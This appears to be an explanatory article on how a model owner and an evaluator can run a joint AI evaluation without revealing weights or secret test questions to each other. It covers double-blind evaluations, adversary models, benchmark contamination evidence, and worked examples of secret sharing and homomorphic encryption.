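# Input privacy in joint analysis: how two organisations can answer questions about an AI model without showing each other their data, code or weights

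## What input privacy is and why a joint analysis needs it

Input privacy is the guarantee that people can process information without being able to read it. For example, the postal service delivers a letter without seeing what is inside the envelope. In artificial intelligence, the guarantee matters most for a joint analysis, a computation that needs confidential material from two or more organisations.

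Suppose a government safety institute has written secret test questions about dangerous biology, a company has built a language model whose inner workings it keeps private, and both want to know how the model scores. The company, as model owner, holds the weights and the inference code. The weights are the numbers, often billions of them, that training has adjusted until the model gives useful replies, and anyone with a copy can run the model. The inference code is the program that loads the weights, takes in a question and calculates the reply. The institute, as evaluator, holds a benchmark, which is a fixed set of questions and a rule for marking the answers. The marking can be automated. *Early lessons from evaluating frontier AI systems*, from the British government's AI Security Institute (UK AISI, called the AI Safety Institute until February 2025), describes using a language model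 to grade open-ended answers against rubrics that experts wrote. To produce a score, the weights, the code and the questions have to be on the same computer, and neither side wants that computer to belong to the other.

Google DeepMind and Singapore's AI safety institute faced this problem in 2026. The institute wanted to test Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite, whose weights Google does not release, using private prompts designed to draw out content that would be harmful in Singapore. Trask, Messing and colleagues (2026) report in *Double Blind Evals* that they ran the test on a machine with encrypted memory. Google saw neither the prompts nor the replies, and the institute never saw the weights, though parts of Google's code stayed closed to inspection. OpenMined, the nonprofit whose PySyft software coordinated the run, says in *PySyft used for first double-blind evaluation of a proprietary, frontier-class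 AI model* that every earlier outside test of a proprietary model had left one side carrying the risk.

### Why a copy is hard to take back

Even with a confidentiality agreement, nothing technical limits what a recipient does with a copy of the other organisation's data, code or weights, and courts or bad publicity can punish misuse only afterwards. Trask, Bluemke and colleagues (2020) call this the copy problem in *Beyond Privacy Trade-offs with Structured Transparency*. A stolen copy of a model's weights runs exactly as well as the original, and Bucknall, Trager and Osborne (2025), in *Position*, put the cost of training the most advanced commercial models at tens of millions of dollars.

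Test questions lose their value differently. If they get into the data for a later training run, the next model may be trained on the answers, and its score would then rise without any gain in ability. In the Gemini paper, Trask and colleagues worry that this could happen by accident as well as through deliberate training on the test. A company may sincerely promise to keep no logs, but a stray record may still end up in training data, and the institute would have little chance of finding out.

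Another problem is that the institute wants only one number, but to get one it can believe, it would ordinarily have to take the whole model and run the test itself. The 2020 paper calls this the bundling problem and illustrates it with a driver's licence. A doorman needs to know only that a customer is old enough, but he sees everything on the card, because a date of birth cut out of it would convince nobody. A score that the company simply announces for its own model is similarly unconvincing.

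### One organisation's secrets, or several

OpenMined's *How to audit an AI model owned by someone else (part 1)* distinguishes two access problems. In the "1st party" problem, an outsider wants an answer about material held by a single organisation. In the "3rd party" problem, the outsider wants to combine material from several organisations that do not trust one another enough to put it in the same place. These are called the "one-organisation" and "several-organisation" problems here because the original labels are easy to confuse.

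*Enabling External Scrutiny of AI Systems with Privacy-Enhancing Technologies* (Beers and Toner, 2025) describes a 2023 study of whether the recommendation algorithm of Dailymotion, a French video platform, favoured sexually suggestive videos. Dailymotion loaded its records onto a secure server and gave the researchers invented data in the same format. The researchers used the invented data to write their code, then submitted the code with an explanation. Dailymotion read the code, allowed it to run on the real records and released the result. The algorithm did not disproportionately amplify highly suggestive content. Dailymotion's review was enough to protect the confidential data because all of it belonged to Dailymotion.

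That procedure breaks down when the outsider also has a secret. If the safety institute sent its biology questions along with its code, the company's reviewer would read them during the review. In 2024, UK AISI and the AI company Anthropic therefore tried using a protected computer that in effect belonged to neither. *Secure Enclaves for AI Evaluation*, by Trask, Yesilyurt and colleagues, describes a deliberately small trial in which the public model GPT-2 stood in for Anthropic's weights and five rows of a public biology dataset stood in for the institute's questions. Nothing confidential was at risk, so the trial is evidence that two organisations can agree on a computation and run it, but much weaker evidence that they would risk real secrets this way. The 2026 Gemini tests provided evidence that they would.

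A joint analysis can also involve data that neither the evaluator nor the model owner has. As OpenMined points out, a film service knows what it recommended at midnight but not whether the viewer then slept badly, because someone else holds the health records.

The traditional solution is a trusted intermediary, a third organisation that takes material from both sides, does the calculation and reports the answer. A suitable intermediary can be hard to find. In OpenMined's example of a hospital and a bank, it would need to know enough about healthcare and banking to judge which uses of the data are proper. Organisations with that knowledge mostly work in one of those industries, so they are likely to have their own interests in the data. Each additional party makes the search harder. The chosen intermediary would also know more than anyone else involved, so the worry about misuse would shift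 to it. Trask and colleagues named this the recursive oversight problem in 2020. Bucknall and colleagues add that model owners would have to give up some control over the evaluation, which is a political obstacle.

Organisations do sometimes find an intermediary they trust with their data. In the other Gemini test, MLCommons, a consortium that maintains benchmarks, trusted staff at AVERI, a nonprofit evaluation institute, with an unreleased set of prompts. The AVERI staff encrypted the prompts, decrypted the replies and judged them. But Trask and colleagues know of no outside evaluator that has ever received a frontier model's weights in readable form in order to keep a benchmark secret, and there is little reason to expect companies to share them more readily with an intermediary.

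*Secure Multiparty Computation for Privacy-Preserving Data Mining* (Lindell and Pinkas, 2009) explains the standard cryptographic definition of security for joint computation, which compares a real procedure with an imaginary one. In the imaginary procedure, an incorruptible outsider takes everyone's inputs and returns only the agreed answers. The real procedure is secure if no attacker can do more harm in it than in the imaginary one. Input privacy technologies try to achieve the same result without needing such an outsider.

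### The five guarantees

Trask and colleagues (2020) use the term "structured transparency" for arrangements that fix in advance who may learn what, when, and what they may do with it. They divide this aim into five guarantees. An arrangement can deliver one and miss another, which is the main reason to judge them separately.

Formally, **input privacy** requires that whoever supplies the computing cannot learn the inputs (such as the questions and the model's weights), the intermediate values or any output meant for someone else. It does not limit what the recipient can infer from the answer.

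**Output privacy** is the guarantee that a reader of the answer cannot work backwards to the inputs. In an example from OpenMined's *Structured Transparency*, a teacher calculates the average age of 1,000 students from encrypted replies that he cannot read. He gets 27, then repeats the survey without one student and gets 26.98. He can now work out the missing student's age, which is 1,000 × 27 minus 999 × 26.98, or about 47. (OpenMined's text mistakenly gives 20.) A model's outputs can reveal private information in a similar way. Evaluators like to see the probabilities a model assigns to each possible next word, because these make scores more precise. Bucknall and colleagues note that the same probabilities can expose undisclosed details such as the model's hidden dimension, roughly the width of its internal layers. Conversely, a teacher who reads every reply and then publishes a heavily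 blurred average protects the output but not the inputs.

**Input verification** is evidence that the inputs were the ones promised. Input privacy makes this evidence harder to get, because the other party cannot inspect the inputs. A company could load a more cautious model than the one it sells, and the institute would receive an accurate score for the wrong model. Bucknall and colleagues see an incentive to do this, since the version that does best in an audit may not be the version that customers most want to use. *Exploring the Relevance of Data Privacy-Enhancing Technologies for AI Governance Use Cases* (Bluemke, Collins and colleagues, 2023) calls the general difficulty the edit problem: a recipient cannot tell whether the holder altered something before passing it on. A company that hands over its weights with a digital signature gives good evidence of where they came from but does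 not keep them private.

In a model evaluation, Bluemke and colleagues write, **output verification** would show that the owner ran exactly the computation the researcher requested. Without it, an engineer could start with the right model and questions but leave out the fifty hardest questions or mark the answers more leniently. OpenMined's *Structured Transparency Continued* also uses the term for checks that a hidden algorithm's results have some desired property, such as fairness, so an agreement should state which meaning applies.

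**Flow governance** determines who may change the arrangement. If the company alone administers the system, it is free to start logging the prompts later, even if the other four guarantees held at the start. OpenMined distinguishes control by one party, consensus (every party has a veto) and threshold schemes (an agreed share of the parties can act). A veto stops either side from making changes alone, but it doesn't prevent mistakes that both sides miss. For example, both organisations could approve code that prints the questions into the results file.

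Some analyses don't need all five components. Trask and colleagues judge that input privacy, output privacy and flow governance would probably be enough for household electricity readings, because nobody gains by falsifying the data. Relying on only those three would be a poor choice for evaluating a commercial model, because the company supplying the model wants a good score.

OpenMined's focus shifted from mainly protecting outputs to protecting inputs as it moved towards such evaluations. In *Designing for Secure Enclave Collaboration*, the designer who led its PyGrid platform recalls that the early work relied chiefly on differential privacy, which adds random noise to results so that no reader can pick out an individual. The designer explains that this method depends on identifying individuals consistently across datasets, which makes little sense when one organisation brings a model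 and another brings questions. The parties needed input privacy and input verification instead. This is one practitioner's account, but the reasoning is sound, because noise that hides one patient among thousands does not help a company whose secret is the entire model.

### What semi-trusted parties might do

Semi-trusted parties are organisations willing to work together on an agreed procedure but not to share their confidential material with each other. The term describes a company and a safety institute reasonably well, but it is too vague to guide the design of a protocol. Cryptographers need a more exact definition for secure multi-party computation (MPC), a family of protocols in which parties compute a result while their inputs stay hidden from one another. They imagine an adversary who controls one or more of the parties, and classify adversaries by what the controlled parties may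 do.

A *semi-honest* party runs the agreed program faithfully, then studies the messages it received for anything more it can learn. In *Security Against Covert Adversaries*, Aumann and Lindell (2010) argue that protection against only this behaviour is weak, because it mostly guards against inadvertent leakage and suits only parties who "essentially trust each other".

A *covert* party will break the rules if it expects to get away with it. Aumann and Lindell introduced this class for settings such as business, politics and diplomacy, where institutions may cheat but cannot risk the embarrassment of being caught. Their definition includes a deterrence factor, ε, between 0 and 1. If a strategy would let a party cheat successfully with probability p, the honest parties must catch it with probability at least ε × p. In their two-party protocol, one side prepares several scrambled copies of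 the calculation and the other opens all but one to check them. With three copies and each bit of input split into three random shares, ε is 1/2, and it rises to about 9/10 with ten copies and ten shares per bit.

Under one of Aumann and Lindell's definitions of security, a party that cheats can learn the other's secret even if it is caught, but under their strongest definition a party that is caught learns nothing. An institute with questions it cannot replace should insist on the strongest definition, because it can't use them again once the company has read them, whatever the company says afterwards.

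A *malicious* party may do anything. It may tamper with messages, supply incorrect data or collude with other corrupted parties, according to *SoK* (2025), a survey of MPC protocols. The UN's handbook on privacy-preserving computation (2023) says that a malicious adversary, unlike a covert one, does not care who notices.

"Semi-trusted" does not mean "semi-honest". The covert model is probably the closest fit for a well-known company and a public institute, since each has a reputation to lose. This argument is weaker when the secret is valuable enough to attract thieves. Lindell and Pinkas describe adversaries who take over a party partway through a computation, as a hacker would, and a hacker has no stake in the company's reputation. Parties handling frontier weights or questions about weapons therefore have reason to plan for malicious behaviour even if they trust each other.

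Lindell and Pinkas write that when there are only two parties, no protocol can stop a malicious one from refusing to take part, substituting a different input, or quitting early, possibly after getting its own answer. The model swap is an input substitution, so even the strongest of these security definitions does not verify inputs. Protocols can guarantee that everyone gets an answer, even if some parties quit early, when more than half of the parties are honest, but two parties who suspect each other can never count on that.

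## Deciding whether both parties' inputs need protection

Protecting two organisations' secrets at once takes a lot of work. Trask and colleagues write that the main bottleneck is now the legal agreements, code review and coordination between teams, rather than the extra computing. Anyone planning a joint analysis should therefore first check whether both sides have something to protect, because a simpler arrangement will usually be enough if only one does.

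### Comparing what each side hides with what the other needs

Bucknall, Trager and Osborne (2025), in *Ensuring mutual privacy is necessary for effective external evaluation*, offer a precise way to check. Call the model owner M and the evaluator E. Each party makes three lists:

- I_M and I_E are what the owner and the evaluator know. Some items, such as the model's name, can appear on both lists.
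- P_M and P_E are the private sets, the parts of its own knowledge that each party wants to keep from the other. An item the other party already knows can't be in a private set.
- R_E is what the evaluator needs from the owner, and R_M is what the owner needs from the evaluator.

The next step is to look for overlaps. The symbol ∩ means "the items that appear in both sets", so P_M ∩ R_E contains everything that the owner wants to hide and the evaluator needs. Likewise, P_E ∩ R_M contains everything that the evaluator wants to hide and the owner needs. If either overlap has something in it, the parties have a privacy problem. If both do, they have a mutual privacy problem. (The paper's verbal explanation of P_M ∩ R_E accidentally swaps the two parties. The explanation here follows the symbols.)

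Bucknall and colleagues count more than facts as information, so a set can also include access to a model or dataset, knowledge of what the other party is doing, or an assurance, such as evidence that a reported version number is accurate. Assurances are easy to leave off the lists, but they are most of what a model owner needs from an evaluator.

### The sets for a secret biology benchmark

For the safety institute and the company from the previous section, the private and required sets might look like this:

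| Set | Contents |
|---|---|
| P_M: the company hides | The weights, the model's architecture, the training methods and data, the way the system generates its replies, details of its safeguards, and any version without safeguards |
| R_E: the institute needs | Replies produced with the real weights, evidence of which version produced them, a version without safeguards, and perhaps next-word probabilities |
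| P_E: the institute hides | The questions, the reference answers and the marking method |
| R_M: the company needs | Assurance that the institute stays within agreed limits and that it will protect anything confidential it receives |

The version of a model without safeguards is clearly an input that evaluators need and the company needs to protect. A commercial model may refuse to answer questions about dangerous biology, and a low score would then be weak evidence of what the model knows. Evaluators who want to measure the upper limit of its abilities therefore ask for a version that does not refuse. The company has good reason to restrict access to that version, because it would also help someone with bad intentions.

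The conflict in P_E ∩ R_M is less obvious, because the company has no direct use for the institute's questions. Bucknall and colleagues explain that the company wants to check that the institute is keeping to the agreed limits, and the easiest way to do so is to watch what the institute does, which reveals the questions.

The result therefore depends on how each party words its needs. A demand to see everything the institute sends to the model conflicts with the institute's secrecy, but a demand to know that only the agreed program will run and that only a score will come out may not. Similarly, the institute can ask for a version number instead of a technical description. Bucknall and colleagues suggest giving each version an arbitrary label that identifies it without revealing how it works. Each party should write its needs as narrowly as it can before comparing the lists.

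Both overlaps can be empty if the parties word the sets narrowly, but some computer still has to process the questions and the weights together. The sets describe only what the parties want to learn, so the parties must separately ask who controls that computer.

The two organisations can also question whether each secret, such as the marking method, needs to be kept. Bucknall and colleagues compare the marking method to the official emissions test that Volkswagen cheated on. Software in some of its cars recognised the test from clues such as the position of the steering wheel, the speed and the air pressure, and changed how the emissions controls worked. An AI company usually knows when a test is taking place and controls the system throughout, so it would not need to detect one. If it knew that an evaluator would count only the share of harmful requests a filter catches, it could raise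 that share by letting the filter block many harmless requests too.

An evaluator's secrecy can make its evaluation worse. Bucknall and colleagues quote Anthropic's comment on an audit by the evaluation group ARC (now METR). After reading the report, Anthropic's staff realised they could have helped ARC find more concerning behaviour if they had known more about its approach. Secrecy also makes it harder for the public to judge how well the evaluator did its job. Bucknall and colleagues reply that companies could instead give evaluators more access and information, and that an accreditation body could check the evaluators' quality. They accept that independent evaluators would sometimes waste time rediscovering what the company already knew. A reasonable compromise is to hide the questions but explain the general method, unless knowing the method would make the test easy to game.

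### Evidence that test questions reach training data

Questions about dangerous biology could help someone cause harm, which is reason enough to protect them. For most other benchmarks, the main worry is that the questions could leak into training data, as described earlier. Researchers call this contamination.

Xu, Wang and colleagues (2024), in *Benchmarking Benchmark Leakage in Large Language Models*, looked for signs of contamination in 31 models using GSM8K and MATH, two public collections of maths problems. Each collection has a training part, which developers can use to improve their models, and a test part, which they should not. The researchers had ChatGPT reword the problems and measured how much better each model predicted the original text than the reworded text. A large gap suggests that the model has seen the original. They then compared the gaps for the training and test parts.

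About half of the models appeared to have used the training part. The evidence that they had used the test part was weaker. In one check, the researchers cut off each problem and its solution at five places and asked the model for the next five tokens (words or pieces of words). Qwen-1.8B, a small model from the Chinese company Alibaba, reproduced all five continuations exactly for 223 training problems from GSM8K, 67 training problems from MATH and 25 test problems from MATH. Trask and colleagues cite this study as strong evidence of leakage in roughly half the models, which is accurate only if "leakage" includes the training parts.

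Public tests have also appeared in the training data of more recent models. SWE-bench Verified is a benchmark of real software bugs from open-source projects that many model developers use as training data. OpenAI's *Why we no longer evaluate SWE-bench Verified* (February 2026) reports that every frontier model tested could reproduce either the original human-written fix or exact details of the problem description for some tasks.

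These findings show that contamination is common when a benchmark is public, but not that any company has trained on confidential questions it received during an evaluation.

The harm from a leaked test depends partly on how many copies end up in a model's training data. In *Test Set Contamination of Generative Evaluations*, Schaeffer, Kazdan and colleagues (2026) trained models with 34 million to 344 million parameters (adjustable numbers) on web text mixed with 0 to 3,162 copies of the MATH test, which has 5,000 problems. With ten copies or fewer, the models scored about as badly as models that had never seen the test. At around 100 copies, their scores jumped to near the maximum.

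The high scores came from memorisation. When the researchers reworded the problems or changed the numbers in them, the scores fell to almost zero. Raising the temperature, which makes a model choose its words more randomly, also lowered the scores of heavily contaminated models. At 1,000 copies, raising it from 0 to 1 cut the score by a factor of about 40. Evaluators could use either altered problems or a higher temperature as a rough check for memorised answers.

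These results are only partly reassuring about accidents. A stray log from one evaluation is closer to one copy than to 100, and it would normally contain the questions and the model's own replies, whereas the copies in the experiment included correct solutions. Further training on fresh data also weakened the effect. But larger models gained more from the same number of copies, and the largest model tested was far smaller than today's commercial models. An evaluator who repeats every question many times for a more precise score would also leave many copies in the log. Schaeffer and colleagues caution that the thresholds may change with scale, so nobody should treat ten copies as a safe limit for a frontier model.

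An evaluator would also struggle to detect a leak afterwards. One measure Xu and colleagues used requires the probabilities a model assigns to words, which companies often withhold. Their check on exact continuations works without them, but it can miss questions that someone reworded or reformatted before training.

### Who is exposed in the simpler arrangements

There are several established ways to run an outside evaluation without special privacy technology. Most of them protect one party by exposing the other.

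| Arrangement | What the evaluator exposes | What the owner exposes |
|---|---|---|
| API access with a no-logging promise | The questions, to the owner | The replies and anything people can infer from them |
| On-site work at the owner's premises | The questions and methods, to the owner | Whatever the visitors see |
| Handing over the weights | Nothing to the owner | A complete copy of the model |
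| A neutral tester | The questions, to the tester | The model, to the tester |
| Remote execution with owner review | The code and any data sent with it, to the owner | The approved result |

**API access.** An API (application programming interface) lets the evaluator's software send questions to a model that stays on the owner's computers. The owner receives the questions in readable form, so the evaluator has to rely on a promise that they won't be stored. Some companies offer certain customers "zero data retention", but Bucknall and colleagues say it is unclear whether evaluators get this option or whether anyone could verify that a company honours it.

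Benchmark designers handle this risk differently. *GUIGuard-Bench* (2026), a privacy benchmark for AI agents that operate computers and phones through the screen, has a hidden test set. Its designers run this set only if the API's operator agrees not to train on the material, inspect it by hand or keep it beyond the temporary logs needed to run the service. The designers of ARC-AGI, a reasoning benchmark, were more cautious with OpenAI's o3 model. They used a "semi-private" set of questions that they accepted might leak and kept their fully private set away from the API, according to Bucknall and colleagues.

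An API also limits what the evaluator can find out. *Expanding External Access To Frontier AI Models For Dangerous Capability Evaluations* (2026) reports that outside evaluators often see only a model's outputs, sometimes with its written reasoning, and get days rather than weeks to work. They have no way to verify much of what companies tell them about the model.

The evaluator can instead work on the owner's premises. OpenMined describes this arrangement at the US government's Federal Statistical Research Data Centers. Researchers with special clearance enter the building without electronic devices, work on a secure computer, hand their code to an analyst and leave without their results. If the project passes review, an employee runs the code and sends the researchers the results.

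This procedure protects the government's data well, and the researchers usually have nothing confidential of their own to protect. The safety institute, however, would have to bring its biology questions into the company's building and enter them on the company's computer, so they would be no better protected than with an API. *Privacy-preserving third-party audits on Unreleased Digital Assets with PySyft*, the British government's case study of OpenMined's software, points out that on-site work also restricts who can do an audit and when.

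**Handing over the weights.** If the evaluator runs the model on its own computers, the owner never sees the questions. This is easy when the weights are public, because the evaluator can download them. With a proprietary model, the owner takes on almost all the risk. Trask and colleagues write that some evaluators get direct access to weights for certain high-stakes tests, such as those that examine a model's internal activity, but mostly when they work for the owner or have a close relationship with it. The evaluator also needs enough computing power and engineering time to run the model, and according to the British case study, its copy may come to differ from the version that customers use.

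A neutral third organisation can hold both the model and the questions. The US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST) launched a programme of this kind, AI Technology Evaluation (AITE), in July 2026. Data providers submit a dataset that nobody else can access and a task to perform on it. Model providers submit models, and NIST runs the tests and publishes the scores. In its road map, NIST (2026) presents itself as a neutral third party and says that sequestering the data prevents contamination.

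AITE is still small. NIST's *AITE Overview* lists three image-based tests, with 641 trials on controlling quantum dots (tiny semiconductor structures that can trap single electrons), 10,000 on checking variants in the human genome and 3,000 on recognising public safety events. The only model it lists is an unnamed open-source example, so the programme has not yet shown that companies will give NIST their most valuable models.

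The FAQ in NIST's *AI Technology Evaluation (AITE)* says that the agency will protect data and models as "controlled unclassified information", an American category for material that is sensitive but not classified. But the road map lists security good enough for operational data in that category as a feature of the finished programme, so a participant should ask which protections are already in place. AITE could suit a hospital that wants to compare models on unpublished scans. It is a poor fit for a classified weapons benchmark or for a company that will not give its weights to anyone. Both sides still have to trust NIST as the intermediary.

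In **remote execution with owner review**, which Dailymotion used, the evaluator writes code using mock assets (invented data or a stand-in model in the real format), and the owner reviews the code before running it. OpenMined proposed this in 2023 as a more flexible kind of API. With an ordinary API, the owner has to build a new function for each new type of question, but here the owner only has to approve a function the evaluator has written. Bucknall and colleagues object that the evaluator has to show its code to the owner.

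### Two remote-execution studies

The Dailymotion study described earlier was part of a project set up after the 2019 terrorist attack on two mosques in Christchurch, New Zealand. By the time the project's first phase ended in November 2023, four outside researchers had sent queries to Dailymotion and LinkedIn. The first collected basic statistics so that the others could plan their studies.

*Private Map-Secure Reduce* (2025) reports that Dailymotion supplied data on 10 million video recommendations and that its data governance team reviewed every query by hand. The main recommendation algorithm, which handled 77% of the traffic, promoted videos with every level of sexual suggestiveness. Two other algorithms handled only videos with suggestiveness scores below 0.5, perhaps because the company wanted to protect advertisers or comply with regulations. OpenMined's *New Research Shows Promise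 for Safe, Secure & Private Auditing* reports that the researchers also found that the top 10% of videos received 75% of recommendations. Outsiders could not have learned this by watching a few videos and noting the site's next suggestions.

LinkedIn required differential privacy for every query, according to OpenDP, the project that supplied the software for this. The data had about 70 million rows, each describing the top post in one user's feed during one session. Sources disagree about whether Dailymotion also required differential privacy. The British case study says that all results had this protection, but *Private Map-Secure Reduce* says that Dailymotion relied on manual approval instead. The second account is more specific about Dailymotion. If it is right, the privacy of Dailymotion's users depended on its staff noticing when a result revealed too much.

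In the other study, EleutherAI, a nonprofit AI research group, stood in for a company with secret training data. OpenMined wanted to find out whether the data contained information about three biological agents: the common soil bacterium *Bacillus subtilis*, the influenza virus, and respiratory syncytial virus (RSV), which is harmless to most adults. These were chosen as mild substitutes for more dangerous pathogens. The dataset had more than 200,000 documents, mostly ordinary web text, and included a non-public collection from UK AISI with many mentions of the three agents.

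The evaluator used mock data to write a keyword search, then submitted the code to EleutherAI, which reviewed it. The search used TF-IDF, a standard method that gives a document a high score if a search term appears often in it and in few other documents. The search flagged about 60 documents. EleutherAI inspected them and gave the evaluator only a summary.

| Search term | Recall | Precision | Share of the dataset returned |
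|---|---|---|---|
| Influenza | 57% | 21% | 0.03% |
| RSV | 60% | 11% | 0.03% |
| Subtilis | 79% | 79% | 0.01% |

Precision is the share of returned documents that were relevant, and recall is the share of relevant documents that the search returned. The search for "subtilis" did well on both, probably because people write the name in fewer ways. For "RSV", only about one in nine returned documents was relevant, and the search missed 40% of the relevant ones. Many of the missed documents were about products and reagents. The results were enough to show that the dataset contained material on the three agents, which was the study's only aim. However, a search this weak could easily miss a handful of dangerous documents in a real audit.

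The researchers could calculate these figures because they already knew which documents were relevant, information an evaluator would not have in a real audit of secret data. EleutherAI therefore recommends that evaluators measure how well their methods work before running them remotely. It leaves input and output verification for future work.

Reading the evaluator's code did no harm in either study. Dailymotion's researchers had no secrets in their queries, and letting EleutherAI see a search for "influenza" revealed nothing sensitive. But if a government institute wanted to search a company's training data for an unpublished method of making a virus more dangerous, the company would read the search terms during its review, and those terms could reveal the method.

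### Whether contracts are enough

A good contract might make technical protection unnecessary. The institute could use the company's API, and the company could promise to delete the questions and accept penalties if it failed. Trask and colleagues, who want evaluators to adopt double-blind testing, acknowledge that contracts and no-logging rules have long kept outside evaluators' prompts confidential. None of the contamination studies above traces a leak to a broken contract. A well-known company also has a reputation to protect, and a contract costs much less than a new technical system.

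Contracts work best against deliberate misuse that somebody can detect. They protect much less against accidental leaks through logs, and compensation will not make leaked questions secret again.

The two sides may also be unable to agree on a strong contract. Most outside evaluations are voluntary, so a company that dislikes the evaluator's terms can refuse to take part. Bucknall and colleagues think this is why evaluators' secrets are often protected less carefully than owners' secrets. They add that a badly written legal requirement for outside evaluation could reverse the imbalance and put the weights at risk.

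Finally, a contract may satisfy the two parties but not outsiders. If a company scores very well on questions that passed through its own computers, sceptics can suspect that it had seen them before, which hurts even an honest company. This matters little for a routine test with replaceable questions, where a contract is probably the sensible choice. The argument for technical protection is much stronger when a leak would be dangerous or when the score has to convince people who distrust the company.

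### A rule for choosing

A simpler arrangement is enough if it exposes only material whose disclosure the holder could tolerate. The parties can apply this rule to the following cases.

1. **Only the owner has a secret.** The evaluator might be using a public benchmark, or code that it is happy to show. API access is enough if the model's replies can answer the question. If the question concerns training data or user records, remote execution with owner review is a better choice.
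2. **Only the evaluator has a secret.** If the weights are public, the evaluator should download them and run the test on its own computers.
3. **Both have secrets, but one side can afford a leak.** An evaluator that can write new questions cheaply could use an API with a no-logging contract and retire the questions afterwards. It could also do what the ARC-AGI designers did and risk only part of its collection. An owner might hand over an old model whose weights no longer have much value.
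4. **Both have secrets they cannot afford to lose, but they trust the same tester.** That tester can hold both sets of material, provided that its security is good enough for the more sensitive of the two.
5. **None of these applies.** Both inputs need technical protection.

The secret biology benchmark falls into the last case unless the institute and the company can find a tester they both trust. The institute cannot let the company read questions that might help someone make a weapon, and the company will not hand over its weights.

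## Computing on encrypted or secret-shared inputs

Cryptography can protect both inputs without a trusted tester or special hardware. In secure multi-party computation (MPC), the company and the institute each hold random-looking pieces of every number and calculate with them. In homomorphic encryption, the institute encrypts its questions and the company calculates on them without decrypting them. Either method can in principle run any model, but work that takes a fraction of a second on readable data can take seconds, minutes or longer. Whether they are practical therefore depends mostly on how much calculation the question needs.

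### From the millionaires' problem to secret sharing

In 1982 the computer scientist Andrew Yao asked how two millionaires could find out which of them is richer without telling each other what they own. Secure multi-party computation (MPC) grew out of this problem. A joint analysis has the same structure, but the private inputs are a model and a set of questions.

Many current systems use additive secret sharing, which splits a number into random shares that add up to it. The sums wrap around at a fixed number, called the modulus, like the hours on a clock. With a modulus of 101, every result lies between 0 and 100, so 108 becomes 7.

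Suppose the company has a weight of 7 and the institute has an input of 12. The company picks 40 at random as its own share of the weight and sends the institute 68, because 40 + 68 = 108, which is 7 modulo 101. The institute learns nothing about the weight from the 68, since any weight from 0 to 100 could have produced it, depending on the company's share. The institute splits its 12 in the same way, keeping 88 and sending the company 25.

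To add the two secrets, the company adds its shares (40 + 25 = 65) and the institute adds its own (68 + 88 = 156, which is 55 modulo 101). Those results add up to 120, which is 19 modulo 101. Multiplying the secrets requires three extra numbers, known as a Beaver triple: a and b, which are random, and c = a × b. A helper called a dealer can create the triple and hand out shares of it before the calculation starts, without seeing the weight or the input.

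| Number | Value | Company's share | Institute's share |
|---|---|---|---|
| Weight | 7 | 40 | 68 |
| Input | 12 | 25 | 88 |
| a | 5 | 60 | 46 |
| b | 9 | 30 | 80 |
| c | 45 | 70 | 76 |

The multiplication then goes as follows:

1. Each party subtracts its share of a from its share of the weight. The company gets 40 − 60 = −20, which is 81, and the institute gets 68 − 46 = 22. They exchange these numbers and add them, which gives 103, or 2. This is the weight minus a.
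2. They do the same with the input and b. The company gets 96, the institute gets 8, and the total is 104, or 3.
3. The company calculates 70 + (2 × 30) + (3 × 60) + (2 × 3) = 316, which is 13.
4. The institute calculates 76 + (2 × 80) + (3 × 46) = 374, which is 71.
5. If they want to see the answer, they add their results: 13 + 71 = 84, which is 7 × 12.

This works because 7 × 12 is (5 + 2) × (9 + 3), or 45 + (2 × 9) + (3 × 5) + (2 × 3). Both parties know the 2 and the 3, and they hold shares of 5, 9 and 45. Only one of them adds the 2 × 3, since otherwise it would count twice.

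The opened differences are safe to reveal as long as nobody knows a or b. If the dealer told the institute that a was 5, the institute could add the opened difference of 2 and get the weight, so the dealer must not collude with either side. Each triple is also safe to use only once. If the company masked another weight with the same a and the difference was 4, the institute would know that this weight was 2 larger than the first. A model with billions of weights therefore needs an enormous supply of prepared random numbers.

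The procedure hid both inputs perfectly, but the institute can still recover the weight by dividing the answer, 84, by its own input, 12, to get 7. (If the product had wrapped around, the institute could have multiplied the answer by 59 modulo 101, because 12 × 59 is 1 modulo 101.) Input privacy does not limit what the answer reveals. *SecDTD* (2026), a paper on faster private inference, says that such protocols normally do not try to conceal the result, because somebody has to be able to use it.

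A real model uses billions of weights to compute each reply, which makes the weights much harder to work out from its replies. The parties can also reduce the risk by keeping intermediate results as shares and revealing only the final score. A later section covers other limits on answers.

### Homomorphic encryption and who holds the key

With homomorphic encryption, the company can turn an encrypted 12 into an encrypted 84 by adding the encrypted number to itself until it has seven copies. It never learns that the input was 12 or that the result is 84. *Fully* homomorphic encryption also allows encrypted numbers to be multiplied together, which makes it possible to run a neural network. Jayashankar, Kim and colleagues (2025), in *Cerium*, describe how this works with CKKS, a popular scheme for calculating with decimals:

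1. The institute creates a secret key, which it keeps, and evaluation keys, which allow the company to calculate but not to decrypt. For a neural network, the evaluation keys typically take up 10 to 50 GB.
2. The institute turns its question into lists of numbers, packs each list into an encrypted object called a ciphertext, and sends the ciphertexts to the company.
3. The company runs the model, using its weights in ordinary readable form. It can add ciphertexts, multiply them, and rotate the numbers inside them to line up the right pairs.
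4. Each ciphertext can go through only a limited number of multiplications in a row. When this budget runs low, the company refreshes the ciphertext with an expensive operation called bootstrapping.
5. The company returns the encrypted result, and the institute decrypts it.

This suits the biology benchmark well in some respects, because the weights never leave the company's computers and the company sees neither the questions nor the replies. But the institute holds the only secret key, so it sees the full result for every question and could try to learn about the weights from those results. The parties could instead use threshold encryption, which splits the key so that neither can decrypt anything alone. Mimee Xu's doctoral dissertation, *Better Incentives* (2025), proposes this for checking whether hospital emergency departments prioritise patients fairly.

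Both methods usually leave the architecture of the company's model visible. Das, Azad and Saxena (2026), in *A Graph-Based Analysis of Comparability, Scale, and Attribution in Private Transformer Inference*, reviewed 62 systems for running transformers, the type of neural network behind current language models, on hidden inputs. "Model privacy" in these systems covers the weights but usually not the architecture. A company that treats its architecture as confidential would have to disclose it to the evaluator or use another method.

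### Why the non-linear steps cost so much

A transformer normally spends most of its running time multiplying large tables of numbers. These multiplications are linear, meaning they use only additions and multiplications by weights. Non-linear steps come between them. Softmax turns a list of scores into positive fractions that add up to 1, GELU mostly suppresses negative numbers, and LayerNorm rescales a list according to how spread out its values are. These steps take little time on readable data, but Das and colleagues found that they take up most of the time once the data is hidden.

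In MPC, a share doesn't show how big the secret is or even whether it is negative. Modulo 101, a system might use 51 to 100 for negative numbers, so that 94 means −7. If the company's share is 40, the institute's share is 68 when the secret is 7 and 54 when it is −7. Neither share shows the sign on its own, so the parties have to work it out together through several rounds of messages. They need similar comparisons to round the result of each multiplication, because MPC systems store decimals as whole numbers.

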